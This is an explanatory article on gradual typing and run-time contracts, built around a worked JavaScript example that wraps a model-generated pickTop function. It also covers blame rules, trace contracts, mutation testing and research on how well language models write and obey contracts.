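# Gradual typing, run-time contracts and the checking of machine-generated code

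## Types, contracts and generated code in brief

Gradual typing and run-time contracts are techniques for checking programs in which some parts deserve more trust than others. Gradual typing is a language design that allows code with type annotations to mix with code that has none, and uses run-time tests to guard the places where the two meet. A contract is an executable condition that a value or function must satisfy, which the language checks while the program runs. Both techniques are older than large language models, which produce text by repeatedly predicting what comes next. They have a new use because programmers now routinely run code from these models beside code that people wrote and tested.

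### A function to ask for

Suppose a programmer asks a model to add a function, pickTop(items, k, score), to a working program. It should return the k items for which score returns the highest values. An online shop might find its three best sellers by calling pickTop with a list of products, the number 3 and a function that looks up a product's sales.

The argument score is itself a function, which pickTop will call. Tanter (2025) gives about the smallest possible example. If f(x) is x + 2 and h(g) is g(1), then h applies any function it is given to 1, so h(f) is 3. Programmers call a function passed in this way a callback.

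The number k must be a whole number between 0 and the number of items. The callback score must return a finite number for each item. The result must have k members, all taken from items, and no omitted item may score higher than an included one. The program that calls pickTop is responsible for k and score, and the generated function is responsible for the result.

### Static and dynamic checking

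A type describes a set of values that share certain operations, such as addition for integers. Siek defines a type error as applying an operation to a value of the wrong type, such as trying to concatenate an integer in a language that concatenates only strings. Languages such as Python and JavaScript check for these errors dynamically, by examining values just before each operation as the program runs. Java and C# do much of this checking statically, using a checker that reads the program's text and reports errors before the program runs.

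No static checker can predict in general which programs will cause a type error when run, because that task is equivalent to the halting problem: deciding whether an arbitrary program ever stops, which is provably unsolvable. Checkers therefore err on the side of rejecting programs. Siek gives the example of a Java program with an ill-typed call in a branch that can never execute. The compiler rejects the program even though it would run without error.

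Jeremy Siek and Walid Taha developed gradual typing in 2006 so that programmers could choose between static and dynamic typing within one language. The type checker checks annotated code before the program runs. A variable without an annotation gets the dynamic type, written ?, which is compatible with every other type, so any checks on its value happen while the program runs.

For pickTop the language might be TypeScript, which adds a static type checker to JavaScript. The function's type then fits on one line:

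```ts
function pickTop<T>(items: T[], k: number, score: (item: T) => number): T[]
```

T stands for any type, such as a product. The line declares a function that takes a list of Ts, a number k, and a callback that takes one T and returns a number. The function returns a list of Ts. From this, the compiler can reject a call that passes the string "three" for k, or a function body that returns k.

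The type signature leaves out most of what the programmer asked for. The type number includes −1 and 2.5, neither of which makes sense as k. It also includes Infinity, which, according to the TypeScript handbook, JavaScript returns for division by zero instead of raising an exception. So a callback that divides a product's revenue by its number of visitors has the right type, but breaks the requirement of a finite score when a product has revenue but no recorded visits. The result type T[] fixes neither the list's length nor its contents, so a pickTop that always returned an empty list would pass the type checker.

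After checking a program, the TypeScript compiler erases the types, so the JavaScript that runs contains none. If plain JavaScript code then calls pickTop with "three", nothing checks the argument's type. Other designs enforce types at run time. In Typed Racket, according to Northeastern University's *A Spectrum of Type Soundness and Performance* (2018), the compiler inserts run-time checks at the boundaries between typed and untyped modules to detect values that do not match the types.

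### Contracts at a boundary

A module is a separately written unit of a program, often a single file, that makes some of its names available to other modules. A boundary is the place where values pass between two modules held to different standards, one typed and the other untyped, or one trusted and the other generated. It is a natural place for a check because everything the untyped or generated module supplies to the other must cross it.

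*Contracts and Boundaries*, part of the guide to the Racket language, starts with a module that exports a value called amount with the contract "positive?". Whenever another module refers to amount, the contract system checks that it is positive and blames the exporting module if it is not. Contracts are code too, and this one contains a mistake. If amount is not a number, "positive?" itself raises an error, because it accepts only numbers. The contract has to check that amount is a number before checking that it is positive.

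Design by contract is the idea that two pieces of software have definite obligations to each other. It owes much to Bertrand Meyer, who built it into the programming language Eiffel. Meyer (1992), in *Applying “Design by Contract”*, explains it with the example of a courier in Paris. The customer must hand over a package of at most 5 kilograms and pay 100 francs, and the courier must deliver it within four hours. Each party's obligation benefits the other, and if the package is too heavy, the courier need not do anything. In software, the customer is the calling code, or client, and the courier is the function, or supplier. The precondition is what the client must ensure before the call, and the postcondition is what the supplier must ensure on return.

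Under Meyer's rule for assigning fault, a broken precondition is a bug in the caller, and a broken postcondition is a bug in the function. If the shop's program asks for the ten best of four products, the bug is in the shop's program, even if the generated code is poor.

Meyer concluded, though many programmers resist the idea, that a test belongs either in the precondition or in the body of the function, never in both, because redundant tests add code that may itself contain bugs. Eiffel's compiler accordingly let programmers choose how much to monitor. By default it monitored only preconditions, partly because a library ready for release is probably more reliable than the new application that calls it. With pickTop the situation is reversed. The caller is established code and the supplier is new, so the postcondition most needs checking.

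The callback complicates this division because, when pickTop calls score, pickTop becomes the client and the shop's program becomes the supplier. A score of Infinity is therefore the shop's fault, even though it appears in the middle of generated code. A check at the start of the call to pickTop can't detect this fault without running score on every item in advance. Instead, a wrapper checks each call to score as it happens. A wrapper is a stand-in for a function that tests every use of it and passes the call on to the original.

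### How a model writes code

A language model writes a program from left to right, one token at a time. Each token comes from a fixed vocabulary and is one or more characters long. *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* (Mündler, He and colleagues, 2025) describes the process as a loop. The model takes the user's request and the code so far, and computes a probability for every token in the vocabulary. The surrounding software draws one token according to those probabilities, appends it to the code, and repeats the process until it draws a special token that marks the end of the text.

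The drawing of tokens, or sampling, has a setting called temperature. *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation* (Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues, 2026) describes sampling at temperature 0 as always picking the most probable token. Higher settings give unlikely tokens a better chance. Generation can also end because it has reached a limit on time or tokens, which may leave the program incomplete. This basic loop never tests whether the text is a valid program. Models have learned the rules of programming languages from their training and mostly follow them, but the procedure doesn't guarantee it.

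Programming languages also have tokens, but they differ from a language model's. A compiler first splits the text into names, operators, numbers and so on by fixed rules, so x+1 is always three tokens, with or without spaces. A model's tokens come from a vocabulary built by merging character sequences that often occur together in a large body of text. *TokDrift* (Li, Deng and Nie, 2025) gives the example of a call to a function named factorial, which the model receives as ".factor" and "ial". With a space after the dot, the model receives the dot and the whole word as separate tokens. The compiler reads both versions the same way, but in this example adding the space changed a model's translation of the program from wrong to correct.

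A checker that runs while code is being generated cannot assume that the last word in the text is complete. In an example from Mündler and colleagues, the unfinished program ends in "parseInt(num", where num is a variable that holds a number and parseInt is a function that expects a string. If the next token is ".toString()", the argument has the right type, because that call turns the number into a string. If the next token is "ber", the name becomes "number", which the program never declared.

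### Three moments for a check

A check can run during generation, on the finished code before it runs, or during execution. Later checks can use more information, but a mistake has more time to do damage before they catch it.

During generation, a check has the request, the code so far, and the names and types declared in it. The rest of the program and the values it will handle do not exist yet. An ordinary compiler would reject almost every unfinished program, so the check must instead determine whether the text can still grow into a valid one. Suppose the model begins the body of pickTop with a loop and, confusing k with the list, starts to write "k.length". The signature has already fixed k as a number, and numbers in JavaScript have no property that begins with an l, so no continuation after "k.l" can make the program valid. A system that constrains generation would keep any token that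 led there out of the mask, the set of tokens it allows at that step. In the tests by Mündler and colleagues, type errors like this one made up on average 94% of the compilation errors in generated TypeScript, and syntax errors only 6%.

A check that runs after the text is finished can examine the whole program, but no run-time values. Suppose pickTop sorts the list with a helper called byScore, and the model never defines byScore. TypeScript lets a program define a function below the place that uses it, so a check during generation should accept the call. Once the text is finished, the compiler can report the missing definition with certainty.

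In *Generative Compilation*, Mündler-Sasahara, Venev and colleagues (2026) measured how much this uncertainty delays error reports. They built a checker for unfinished programs in Rust, a language with unusually strict rules, and replayed 961 faulty files through it. The median report came 3 lines after the location the compiler would give for the error, compared with 89 lines for a compiler that waited for the end of the file. Some reports came much later, and 90.5% of the slowest quarter concerned names, imports or functions that could still have appeared later in the file.

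The language also determines when an error is caught. *Unreliable in Practice* (Nogueira, Vieira and Campos, 2026) classified 86,726 generated programs that failed to compile or crashed. Undeclared variables made up between 3.8% (in Rust) and 15.7% (in Java) of compilation errors. Most of the seven models were small or old, so these proportions may not hold for current ones. The study excluded interpreted languages such as Python because an undeclared variable in those languages may cause no error until the program runs.

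Static analyzers search code for suspicious patterns without running it, but even a program's complete text does not reveal what its author wanted, which is a constant problem for these tools. In *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation*, Lunghi, Djire and colleagues (2026) ran an analyzer after each line that a model wrote and passed its warnings back to the model. One set of tasks required a web server to accept connections from outside, a setting that the analyzer has a rule against. In 79 of 83 cases the models removed the setting and broke the program, although their instructions gave the task priority.

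During execution, the actual items, the value of `k`, whatever `score` returns, and the result are all available to check. A check at this point can catch the mistake that a reader of `pickTop` might most easily overlook.

```ts
return [...items].sort((a, b) => score(a) - score(b)).slice(0, k);
```

The line copies the list, sorts it by score and keeps the first k items. It compiles and every type is right, but it sorts from low to high, so it returns the worst sellers. Given three products with scores of 3, 9 and 5, and k equal to 1, it returns the product that scores 3, and a check of the postcondition finds an omitted item that scores 9.

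Even strong models still often write programs that compile but are wrong. Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues tested Claude Opus 4.8, a frontier model of mid-2026, on a deliberately hard set of translations from C to Rust and let it repair its drafts using the compiler's error messages. The share of programs that failed to compile fell from 51.8% to 7.5%, but only 61.0% passed their tests, so nearly a third compiled but failed their tests.

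A run-time check can find such faults, but only on the calls that expose them. If all three products have the same score, or if the shop asks for all three, the reversed sort gives an acceptable answer and the check passes.

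## Write a contract and attach it to a generated function

A contract can test k at the start of the call to pickTop, but it must check score, which is a function, one call at a time. By Rice's theorem, a close relative of the halting problem, no general procedure can decide what a function will do. Dimoulas, Tobin-Hochstadt and Felleisen (2012), in *Complete Monitors for Behavioral Contracts*, give this as the reason contract systems monitor a function's calls instead of testing the function once.

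In *Contracts for Higher-Order Functions*, Findler and Felleisen (2002) showed how to check higher-order contracts, which are contracts on functions that take or return other functions, at run time. Their system tests plain values such as numbers immediately. It puts a function in a wrapper that tests the actual argument when the function is called and the actual result when it returns. Every failure therefore comes with a particular value that broke the contract, and the error message can show it.

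A wrapper stays on score wherever the function is passed or stored. Checks added by hand where pickTop calls score could miss other calls, because pickTop might pass score to a sorting routine or store it in a global variable for other code to call later. Findler and Felleisen met this problem in DrScheme, a programming environment whose extensions supply functions that build panels for its preferences window. DrScheme stores these functions and calls them only when the user opens the window. In general, nobody can find all such calls, and some are in collaborators' code whose source is unavailable.

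### The wrapping rule

Each wrapper carries two labels: p for the party that supplies the value, and n for the party that uses it. Two equations then define the system for functions of one argument:

```text
wrap(test, v, p, n)   =  v if test(v) holds, otherwise an error that blames p
wrap(A → R, f, p, n)  =  x ↦ wrap(R, f(wrap(A, x, n, p)), p, n)
```

A → R is the contract of a function whose argument must satisfy A and whose result must satisfy R. The second equation replaces f with a new function that takes an argument x, wraps it with A, calls f, and wraps the result with R. The labels are swapped when x is wrapped, because the party that uses f supplies its argument. The Racket documentation explains the swap by following the values. The function passes from the module that defines it to the module that calls it, the argument passes back, and the result passes in the same direction as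 the function.

With a callback, the labels swap twice, once for score, which the shop supplies, and again for whatever the generated code passes to score. Findler and Felleisen turn this into a rule that counts how many arrows each condition is to the left of. Leaving out items and k, the contract of pickTop has the shape (item → finite number) → list. The condition "item" is to the left of two arrows, "finite number" is to the left of one, and "list" is to the left of none. The module that supplies the function is responsible for a condition if its count is even, and the caller is responsible if it is odd.

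The second equation assumes that f is a function. In Findler and Felleisen's model, a type system guarantees this. The model in Moy's *Contracts and Effects* (2025) has no types, so it needs another rule that blames p for supplying anything other than a function. JavaScript needs the same check.

### A contract for pickTop

JavaScript has no built-in contract system, but a programmer can write the wrappers as ordinary code. In the code below, guard takes the generated pickTop and returns a checked version. The helper blame(party, reason) throws an error that names the party.

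```js
function guard(pickTop) {
  return (items, k, score) => {
    if (!Array.isArray(items)) blame("shop", "items is not a list");
    if (!Number.isInteger(k) || k < 0 || k > items.length)
      blame("shop", "k is out of range");
    if (typeof score !== "function") blame("shop", "score is not a function");

    const watch = user => item => {
      if (!items.includes(item)) blame(user, "score received a non-item");
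      const s = score(item);
      if (!Number.isFinite(s)) blame("shop", "score gave no finite number");
      return s;
    };

    const result = pickTop(items, k, watch("generated code"));

    if (!Array.isArray(result) || result.length !== k
        || !result.every(x => items.includes(x)))
      blame("generated code", "the result is not k of the items");
    const rate = watch("contract");
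    const omitted = items.filter(x => !result.includes(x));
    if (Math.max(...omitted.map(rate)) > Math.min(...result.map(rate)))
      blame("generated code", "an omitted item scores higher");
    return result;
  };
}
```

The first three tests are the precondition. The function `watch` builds a wrapper for `score`, and its parameter `user` is the label of the wrapper's caller. After `pickTop` returns, the postcondition tests the length and members of the result, then compares the best omitted score with the worst included one. The shop's program should use only the checked version, since a direct call to the original skips every test.

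Suppose the shop has three products with sales of 3, 9 and 5, it asks for the single best, and the model has written this:

```js
const order = items.map((_, i) => i).sort((a, b) => score(b) - score(a));
return order.slice(0, k).map(i => items[i]);
```

The code sorts positions in the list, but it passes the position itself to score instead of the product at that position. At the first comparison, sort calls the wrapper with a number such as 0. Because that number is not one of the items and the label for user is "generated code", guard blames the generated code, and the shop's own function never runs.

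Without the contract, the bug would raise no error. The number 0 has no sales figure, so score returns undefined, the subtraction yields NaN (JavaScript's "not a number"), and sort treats every pair as equal. The function then returns the first product on the list, which sold 3. TypeScript's checker would have rejected the call because a position is not a T, but only if someone had run the generated code through it.

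Now suppose the generated code is correct, but the shop's score function reads its figures from a text file and returns the string "9" instead of the number 9. The generated code calls the wrapper with a product, which passes the first test. The wrapper then calls score, receives "9", and blames the shop because "9" is not a finite number. A programmer who saw only the call stack would find pickTop in it and might ask the model to rewrite pickTop, even though it was correct.

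In Moy's model, an error discards the rest of the computation, so nothing can hide it, but JavaScript code can catch errors. If the generated function calls score inside a try block and continues after any failure, the shop never sees the report. To prevent that, guard could record each failure in its own variable before throwing the error, then check the variable after pickTop returns.

### Postconditions that use the arguments

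The permitted range of k depends on items, and the postcondition of pickTop uses all three arguments. Findler and Felleisen call such contracts dependent. Their example is a square-root function whose result, when squared, must come within 0.01 of the argument. Racket's *Function Contracts* describes a notation, ->i, for contracts of this kind. In it the contract for pickTop is much shorter:

```racket
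(->i ([items list?]
      [k (items) (integer-in 0 (length items))]
      [score (items) (-> (λ (x) (member x items)) finite?)])
     [result (items k score) (top-of items k score)])
```

The names in parentheses after k, score and result are the arguments that each condition uses. The programmer writes finite? and top-of as ordinary functions, and Racket supplies the wrappers and the labels.

A postcondition that calls score can misuse it. Suppose its search for the best omitted item runs one step past the end of the list and calls score(undefined). Neither the shop nor the generated code made that call. Language designers have proposed three ways of handling such a call, named lax, picky and indy, which differ only in which version of score the postcondition receives.

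- Under lax monitoring, the postcondition receives the original, unwrapped score. The bad value goes straight into the shop's function, which may crash or return nonsense. Findler and Felleisen took this course because they regarded the contract as part of the specification and so as correct by definition.
- Under picky monitoring, which Matthias Blume and David McAllester proposed in 2006, the postcondition receives the wrapper that the system made for pickTop. The wrapper catches the misuse but blames the generated code for it.
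- Under indy monitoring, the postcondition gets a second wrapper that names the contract itself as the user, so the contract takes the blame.

The guard function above is indy because it defines rate as watch("contract"). Defining rate as score would make it lax, and defining it as watch("generated code") would make it picky.

*Correct Blame for Contracts* (Dimoulas, Findler and colleagues, 2011) compares the three on two small programs. In the first, a server module supplies a function that applies its argument to 42. The client passes in a function that the contract restricts to positive arguments, but the postcondition mistakenly applies that function to 0. In the second, the same faulty contract covers a function that the client supplies.

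| Monitoring | Faulty contract on the server's function | Faulty contract on the client's function |
|---|---|---|
| lax | no error, result 42 | no error, result 42 |
| picky | blames the server | blames the client |
| indy | blames the contract | blames the contract |
| +indy | blames the server | blames the server |
| −indy | blames the client | blames the client |

Dimoulas and his co-authors proved that lax and indy monitoring never blame a party that had no control over the offending value, while picky monitoring sometimes does. This standard turned out to be too weak for contract systems, because a system that ignored every contract would also meet it. The 2012 paper therefore added complete monitoring, which requires that values pass between parties only under the control of a contract. Lax monitoring doesn't meet that requirement, so indy is the only one of the three that meets both.

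The last two rows of the table treat the contract as part of one of the modules. Racket uses +indy for contracts on a module's exports, on the assumption that whoever wrote the module also wrote its contracts. That assumption is wrong for pickTop, because the shop's programmer writes the contract and a model writes the code. Under +indy, a mistake in the programmer's postcondition would count as a fault in the generated function. Either −indy or a separate label for the contract avoids this, and the separate label is safer if a model also helped write the contract.

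### Data that can change

The guard function has a hole, which this version of pickTop exposes:

```js
items.sort((a, b) => score(a) - score(b));
items.length = k;
return items;
```

The code sorts the shop's own list from low to high, cuts it down to k items and returns it. With k equal to 1, the list now contains only the product that sold 3. No omitted items remain in the list for the postcondition to check, so the worst seller passes as the best. The shop has also lost two products from its list.

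Findler and Felleisen's dependent contracts offer a remedy, because the code that builds the postcondition runs before the function and can save the data's state for later comparison. They used this in DrScheme to stop an extension from removing other extensions' panels. In guard, it is enough to give pickTop a copy of the list and keep the original for the postcondition. However, the copy holds the same product objects, so the generated code could still set a product's sales to zero.

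Copying doesn't work where both sides are supposed to see each other's changes. *Chaperones and Impersonators* (Strickland, Tobin-Hochstadt and colleagues, 2012) handles this case in Racket with wrappers that check every read and write. Checking the whole list at the boundary proves little if another thread or a callback can change it afterwards. In one example, a function replaces the numbers in a list with running totals. The wrapper blames the client, which supplied the list, if the function reads a non-number, and blames the function's module if the function writes one.

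Racket has two kinds of wrapper for this. A chaperone may raise an error, but otherwise it must return the same value as the original object, possibly inside another chaperone. Racket enforces this by comparing the two values after each operation. An impersonator may return something different, but it may only wrap data that can change.

Strickland and colleagues justify the restriction with the example of a graphics library. Whenever the library creates a window element, it checks that the element's parent is either another element or nothing. It later follows the chain of parents without checking again. If a contract between two unrelated modules could replace a parent with some other value, the library would crash on data it had already checked.

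For pickTop, a chaperone that rejects all writes to items would stop the code above as soon as sort tried to move a product, and would blame the generated code. An impersonator can enforce a stricter contract by hiding each product in an opaque package before pickTop receives it. The wrappers for score and for the result unpack it again. The function can then only score a product, move it around and return it, as the type variable T in its signature requires. If the shop's items are small numbers, guard can accept a position in the list as an item, but the stricter contract would reject the position because it is not in a package.

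JavaScript's counterpart is the Proxy object, which can intercept reads and writes. A proxy is not identical to the object behind it, so items.includes(x) returns false when items contains the object and x is its proxy, or the reverse. Racket's equality test can treat a chaperone as equal to the value it wraps.

### Rules about several calls

Some requirements concern the order of calls. *Temporal Higher-Order Contracts* (Disney, Flanagan and McCarthy, 2011) gives four requirements for a function sort(list, cmp), which, like pickTop, takes a callback. Ordinary contracts can express the first two, which limit the arguments of sort and cmp. The third forbids calling sort again before an earlier call has returned, so cmp must not call sort. The fourth allows calls to cmp only until sort returns.

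Enforcing the fourth requirement takes more than watching the calls that sort itself makes, because sort might pass cmp to a third module that calls cmp later. If that happens, the system built by Disney and colleagues blames sort, even though sort neither made nor received the late call. In guard, a variable that records whether pickTop is still running would let the wrapper for score detect late calls. The wrapper would check the variable at each call and blame the generated code if pickTop had already returned.

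An ordinary contract is memoryless, as Moy puts it in *Trace Contracts*, the documentation for a Racket library not yet officially released. The library implements the design in Moy and Felleisen's *Trace contracts* (2023). A trace is the sequence of values that pass through chosen points, such as a function's results, and a trace contract is a condition on that sequence.

Moy and Felleisen's opening example comes from a 2020 bug report. Racket's documentation described a function as returning the total memory allocated since the program started, including memory since reclaimed. Such a total can never fall, but a developer's plot of it showed periodic dips. The trace contract collects the results and tests whether they are in ascending order. If calls return 100, 200 and then 0, the third call fails and the error message blames the function. Testing the whole sequence after every call takes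 time that grows with the square of the number of calls, so the practical version stores only the latest result and compares the next one with it. Moy and Felleisen measured the fixed overhead of trace contracts at between 1% and 17% on average.

Moy and Felleisen also wrote a trace contract for Racket's drawing library, where a program must start a document, start a page, draw, end the page and end the document, in that order. A wrong order can cause undefined behavior in the underlying C code. A regular expression, a notation for patterns in sequences, can describe the permitted order. But the contract runs after every call, when the document is usually unfinished, so the pattern must also accept every incomplete sequence that could still become valid.

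A trace contract would fix another weakness of guard. Suppose score looks up sales in a database that other programs update. If a sale comes in after pickTop has ranked the products correctly but before the postcondition calls score again, guard checks the old choice against the new figures and may blame the generated code for a correct answer. A contract that recorded each item with its score could detect that the same item had received two different scores, and blame the shop.

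Moy and Felleisen use a similar record for a compiler function that must never return a smaller set when given a larger one. The check rejects a result that differs from an earlier one for the same input. They store the input-result pairs in a search tree, so checking n calls takes time proportional to n log n, compared with n³ for a plain list.

### What a contract cannot settle

Findler and Felleisen point out that contracts can guarantee stronger properties than types, but only for the runs in which those properties are checked. A type checker's weaker guarantees hold for every run. *Static Contract Checking for Haskell* gives an example in which a faulty callback escapes detection. The contract for a function f1 requires a callback that returns zero or more for any whole number, and requires f1 to return zero or more as well. The function calls the callback on 1 and subtracts 1 from the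 result. The caller supplies a callback that subtracts 1 from its argument. The callback returns 0 for 1, which is allowed, so f1 returns −1 and is blamed. The callback also breaks its contract, since it would return −1 for 0, but f1 never calls it on 0.

A contract on the result cannot establish that pickTop always returns, because a postcondition runs only after the function has finished. If pickTop loops forever, guard waits forever and reports nothing. Always returning is a liveness property, which requires that something eventually happens. Disney and colleagues check only safety properties, whose violations occur at a definite moment.

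A programmer can sometimes replace a liveness property with a stricter safety property. For example, the wrapper for score could raise an error after a million calls, although this would not stop a loop that never calls score. In *Effectful Software Contracts*, Moy, Dimoulas and Felleisen (2024) mention size-change contracts, which guarantee termination by a more general method. They also warn that contracts alone do not provide security. If pickTop deletes a file and then returns the right products, every test in guard still passes.

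A contract can also change the behaviour of the program it checks, because its conditions are ordinary code. Strickland and colleagues note that the code behind a chaperone can print, modify global variables or alter the arguments passed through it. The postcondition of pickTop calls score again for every item. If score also records each lookup as a page view, adding the contract inflates the shop's page-view count.

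The standard indy rule wraps each argument twice, once for the function and once for the postcondition, so a condition on an argument can run twice. King (2016), in *->i applies contract projections multiple times?*, asked on Racket's mailing list why this was necessary, since both wrappers seemed to assign the same blame under +indy. The repetition only takes extra time if the condition just examines a value, but it gives the wrong count if the condition counts calls. Moy (2025) concluded that the traditional model of higher-order contracts is incompatible with side effects, and built a new model.

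Moy, Dimoulas and Felleisen designed a language in 2024 that prevents such interference. Ordinary code and contract code have separate mechanisms for side effects, and a contract's effects can pass values only to other contract code. They proved that a contract can affect a run only by stopping it with an error. Disney and colleagues had reached a similar guarantee by giving their monitors a record of calls and returns, but no access to functions or mutable data. Such a monitor could not call score, so it would have to check the result of pickTop against the scores already returned to the generated code, and treat any item that the code never scored as a fault.

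## Test whether the contract says enough

A wrapper enforces only the conditions its author wrote. Suppose the contract for pickTop required only that the result be a list of k members of items. A version that ignores score and returns the first k products would pass on every call, and the shop would advertise slow sellers as its favourites.

Even software with a mathematical proof of correctness can have this gap, because the proof shows only that the code meets its specification. In *DafnyCert*, Silva, Amaral and colleagues (2026) describe such a gap in IronFleet, a distributed system with a proof of this kind. Its specification did not require each request to take effect exactly once, so when researchers disabled the code that filters out repeated requests, the faulty system still passed verification.

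### Five wrong versions of pickTop

Mutation testing looks for such gaps by running a check on wrong programs. These are called mutants because a tool usually creates them by making small changes to a correct program. The check's mutation score is the share of mutants it rejects. The example for pickTop uses three products with sales of 3, 9 and 5, in that order, and sets k to 2. The right answer is the products that sold 9 and 5. The table identifies each product by its sales.

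| Wrong version of pickTop | Result | Clause of guard that rejects it |
|---|---|---|
| returns the first k items | 3, 9 | no omitted item scores higher |
| sorts from low to high | 3, 5 | no omitted item scores higher |
| sorts correctly but returns the whole list | 9, 5, 3 | the result has k members |
| returns sales figures instead of products | the numbers 9 and 5 | every member comes from items |
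| returns the best item k times | 9, 9 | none |

The short contract rejects two of the five versions, and `guard` rejects four. `guard` accepts the last version because neither omitted product outsells the one that appears twice.

The obvious repair is a clause that forbids repeats. That raises the score to five out of five, but the clause is wrong. Suppose items is the list of numbers [9, 9, 5] and each number is its own score. The two best items are 9 and 9, which the new clause rejects. Meanwhile, guard accepts 9 and 5, because both values occur in the result and so it finds no omitted items. A version of pickTop that removes duplicates before sorting would therefore pass. The following code instead crosses each returned item off a copy of the list:

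```js
const omitted = [...items];
for (const x of result) {
  const i = omitted.indexOf(x);
  if (i < 0) blame("generated code", "not an item, or returned too often");
  omitted.splice(i, 1);
}
```

It replaces `guard`'s membership test and the line that computed `omitted`. If the result is 9 and 5, a 9 remains in `omitted`, and the last clause catches the error.

A perfect mutation score shows only that the contract catches the mutants someone tried. The score also depends on the test inputs. For example, a mutant that returns the best item k times is correct when k is 1, so only a larger k can expose it.

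Silva and colleagues work with Dafny, a language whose verifier tries to prove that a function meets its contract for every permitted input. A contract is strong if its postcondition allows exactly one result for each permitted input, and weak if it allows more than one for some permitted input. A contract is infeasible if the postcondition allows no result for some permitted input, because no program can meet it. If the precondition permits no input at all, the contract is vacuous.

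Silva and colleagues show that a contract is weak by supplying a second program that also passes verification, and an input on which the two programs differ. One of their examples computes how many rungs to add to a ladder so that no step is too long. Its postcondition requires only that the answer not be negative, so a program that always returns 0 also passes verification. The original program returns 462 for a ladder with a single rung at height 463 and a maximum step of 1.

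By this definition, even the repaired contract for pickTop is weak. It allows the result to be in any order and does not specify which products to return when sales are equal. The programmer may want that freedom, but if the shop prints the result as a ranking, the contract should specify the order. No tool can determine whether the order matters, because the request did not specify one.

### Too weak in one place, too strong in another

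A mutation score does not show which clause to change. *Spec-Harness* (Misu, Lopes and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a Java function that swaps the case of a letter and returns any other character unchanged. A model wrote a contract for this function whose precondition is too strong, because it forbids characters such as "+", which the function handles correctly. The postcondition is too weak, because it requires only that a lowercase letter become some capital letter, which would allow "a" to become "Q".

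This contract rejected 36% of 33 mutants. Removing the faulty precondition raised the score only to 39%. An empty contract scored 9%, because the method counts every failed proof as a detection and the verifier could not prove a range check in the mutated code. An exact postcondition scored 94% rather than 100% because two mutants behave just like the original. A programmer could not tell from these numbers alone what to repair or when to stop.

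Misu and colleagues therefore give the precondition and the postcondition two scores each, one for accepting what it should and one for rejecting what it should. For pickTop, that means trying permitted arguments (including an empty list and k equal to 0), forbidden arguments such as −1 and 2.5, right results and wrong results. If the author had written k > 0 by mistake, only the permitted arguments would expose the error, because guard would blame the shop for a legitimate request for no products. A clause that is too strict produces false alarms that someone will investigate, while a clause that is too weak is harder to notice because it produces no message.

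### Do models check their input?

HumanEval+ and MBPP+ are collections of small Python tasks. Many of their reference solutions begin with assertions about the input, but the usual tests never violate these assertions. *ContractEval* (Lim, Hahn and colleagues, 2025), a benchmark first released as PACT, includes tests that do. A model translated the assertions into logical constraints, and a solver searched for inputs that violate some of them while satisfying the others. The researchers kept an input only if the reference solution ran normally on it with the assertions removed, so that an unrelated crash could not be mistaken for a contract check. This left 364 tasks.

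Five small open models then wrote programs for these tasks. With the ordinary prompts, their programs passed the usual tests on 75–82% of tasks but rejected none of the bad inputs. When the prompt stated the input rules, the programs rejected 23–41%. Adding a few examples of bad input raised this to 49–53%, but the share passing the usual tests fell to 70–73%. In a preliminary trial, examples without the rules had no effect.

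One task required a non-empty string and a second string of length one. A model given these rules checked both lengths but not whether the arguments were strings. After seeing that the call remove_Occ(2.0, 3.0) should fail, it checked the types as well.

The zero is not as bad as it looks, because the ordinary prompts included no request for input checks. Meyer's rule against testing a condition twice also means that pickTop should not check k if guard already does. The result matters more for generated code that runs without a wrapper, where a programmer who wants input checks has to ask for them, preferably with examples, and then test whether they work.

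### Do models write adequate contracts?

In *Beyond Postconditions*, Richter and Wehrheim (2025) asked three models to write a contract for each of the 164 HumanEval+ tasks from its signature and description. They then ran CrossHair, a tool that searches for inputs that break a Python program's assertions, for up to 60 seconds on each contract to look for a fault. A contract was faulty if its precondition permitted an input that the reference precondition forbids, or if its postcondition rejected a correct result.

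CrossHair found no fault in 81.1% of GPT-5's contracts. When the prompt asked only for a postcondition, the figure was 13.0%, mainly because the contracts did not exclude inputs the functions were not meant to handle. One function returns the largest prime factor of n and assumes n is greater than 1 and not prime. Without that precondition, CrossHair reported a bug in the correct solution for n = 1.

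Many of the contracts that passed were too weak. Richter and Wehrheim tested them on incorrect programs written by an earlier model, with a median of 55 per task. Only 39.5% of GPT-5's fault-free contracts rejected all the incorrect programs for their task. From a separate set of 31 real bugs in solutions to programming exercises, CrossHair found 14 using GPT-5's contracts. Even with contracts written by people, it could confirm only 19.

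Chen, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *CodeSpecBench*, also found that models tend to write weak contracts, this time for 2,494 self-contained programming puzzles. GPT-5-mini did best of the 15 models. Of its contracts, 82.0% accepted every valid test case and 59.7% rejected every invalid one, but only 47.0% did both.

On 500 issues from large existing codebases, the contracts tended instead to be too strict. The best model there, Claude 4.5 Sonnet, wrote contracts that rejected the known faulty behaviour in 57.2% of cases but accepted the correct behaviour in only 37.4%. Its contracts did both in 20.2% of cases. Because pickTop is self-contained, a programmer reviewing a model's contract for it should look first for missing clauses. If the function depended on much of the shop's other code, excessive strictness would be the more likely fault.

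A low score may also reflect the difficulty of the test. *How Powerful Are LLMs in Generating Formal Program Specifications?* (Yang, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested how well models write specifications in Rocq, a system for machine-checked proofs. A specification passed if a model could prove that it allowed every correct output tested, and could not prove that it allowed a wrong one. Gemini 3 Pro Preview did best, with 28%. But even when experts wrote the specifications, the best model could prove for only 30% of them that all the correct outputs were allowed. The low score may therefore reflect the models' difficulty with proofs as much as weak specifications. An executable contract like guard avoids this problem, because testing it on an example takes only a function call.

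A model's contract can pass verification without being useful. Misu and colleagues collected 14,936 contracts for Java methods that had passed verification, nearly all of them written by models. Of these, 22.7% had no postcondition, and in 5.6% of cases the model had changed the code it was supposed to describe.

### Contracts written before the code

A model can also write a contract as a plan for its own program. Gidey, Yang and colleagues (2026) tested this in *Better Specifications, Better Code* with five open models on 1,007 competitive programming tasks. They fine-tuned each model on about 2,000 tasks paired with contracts, had it write a contract for each new task, and let it review and repair that contract. The model without fine-tuning then wrote the program from the task and the contract. Nothing enforced the contract when the program ran.

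The share of programs that passed all their tests rose for all five models, but only by 1.5 to 3.3 percentage points. For Qwen3.5-27B, it rose from 19.7% to 21.2%. Contracts from the models without fine-tuning raised the share by at most one point.

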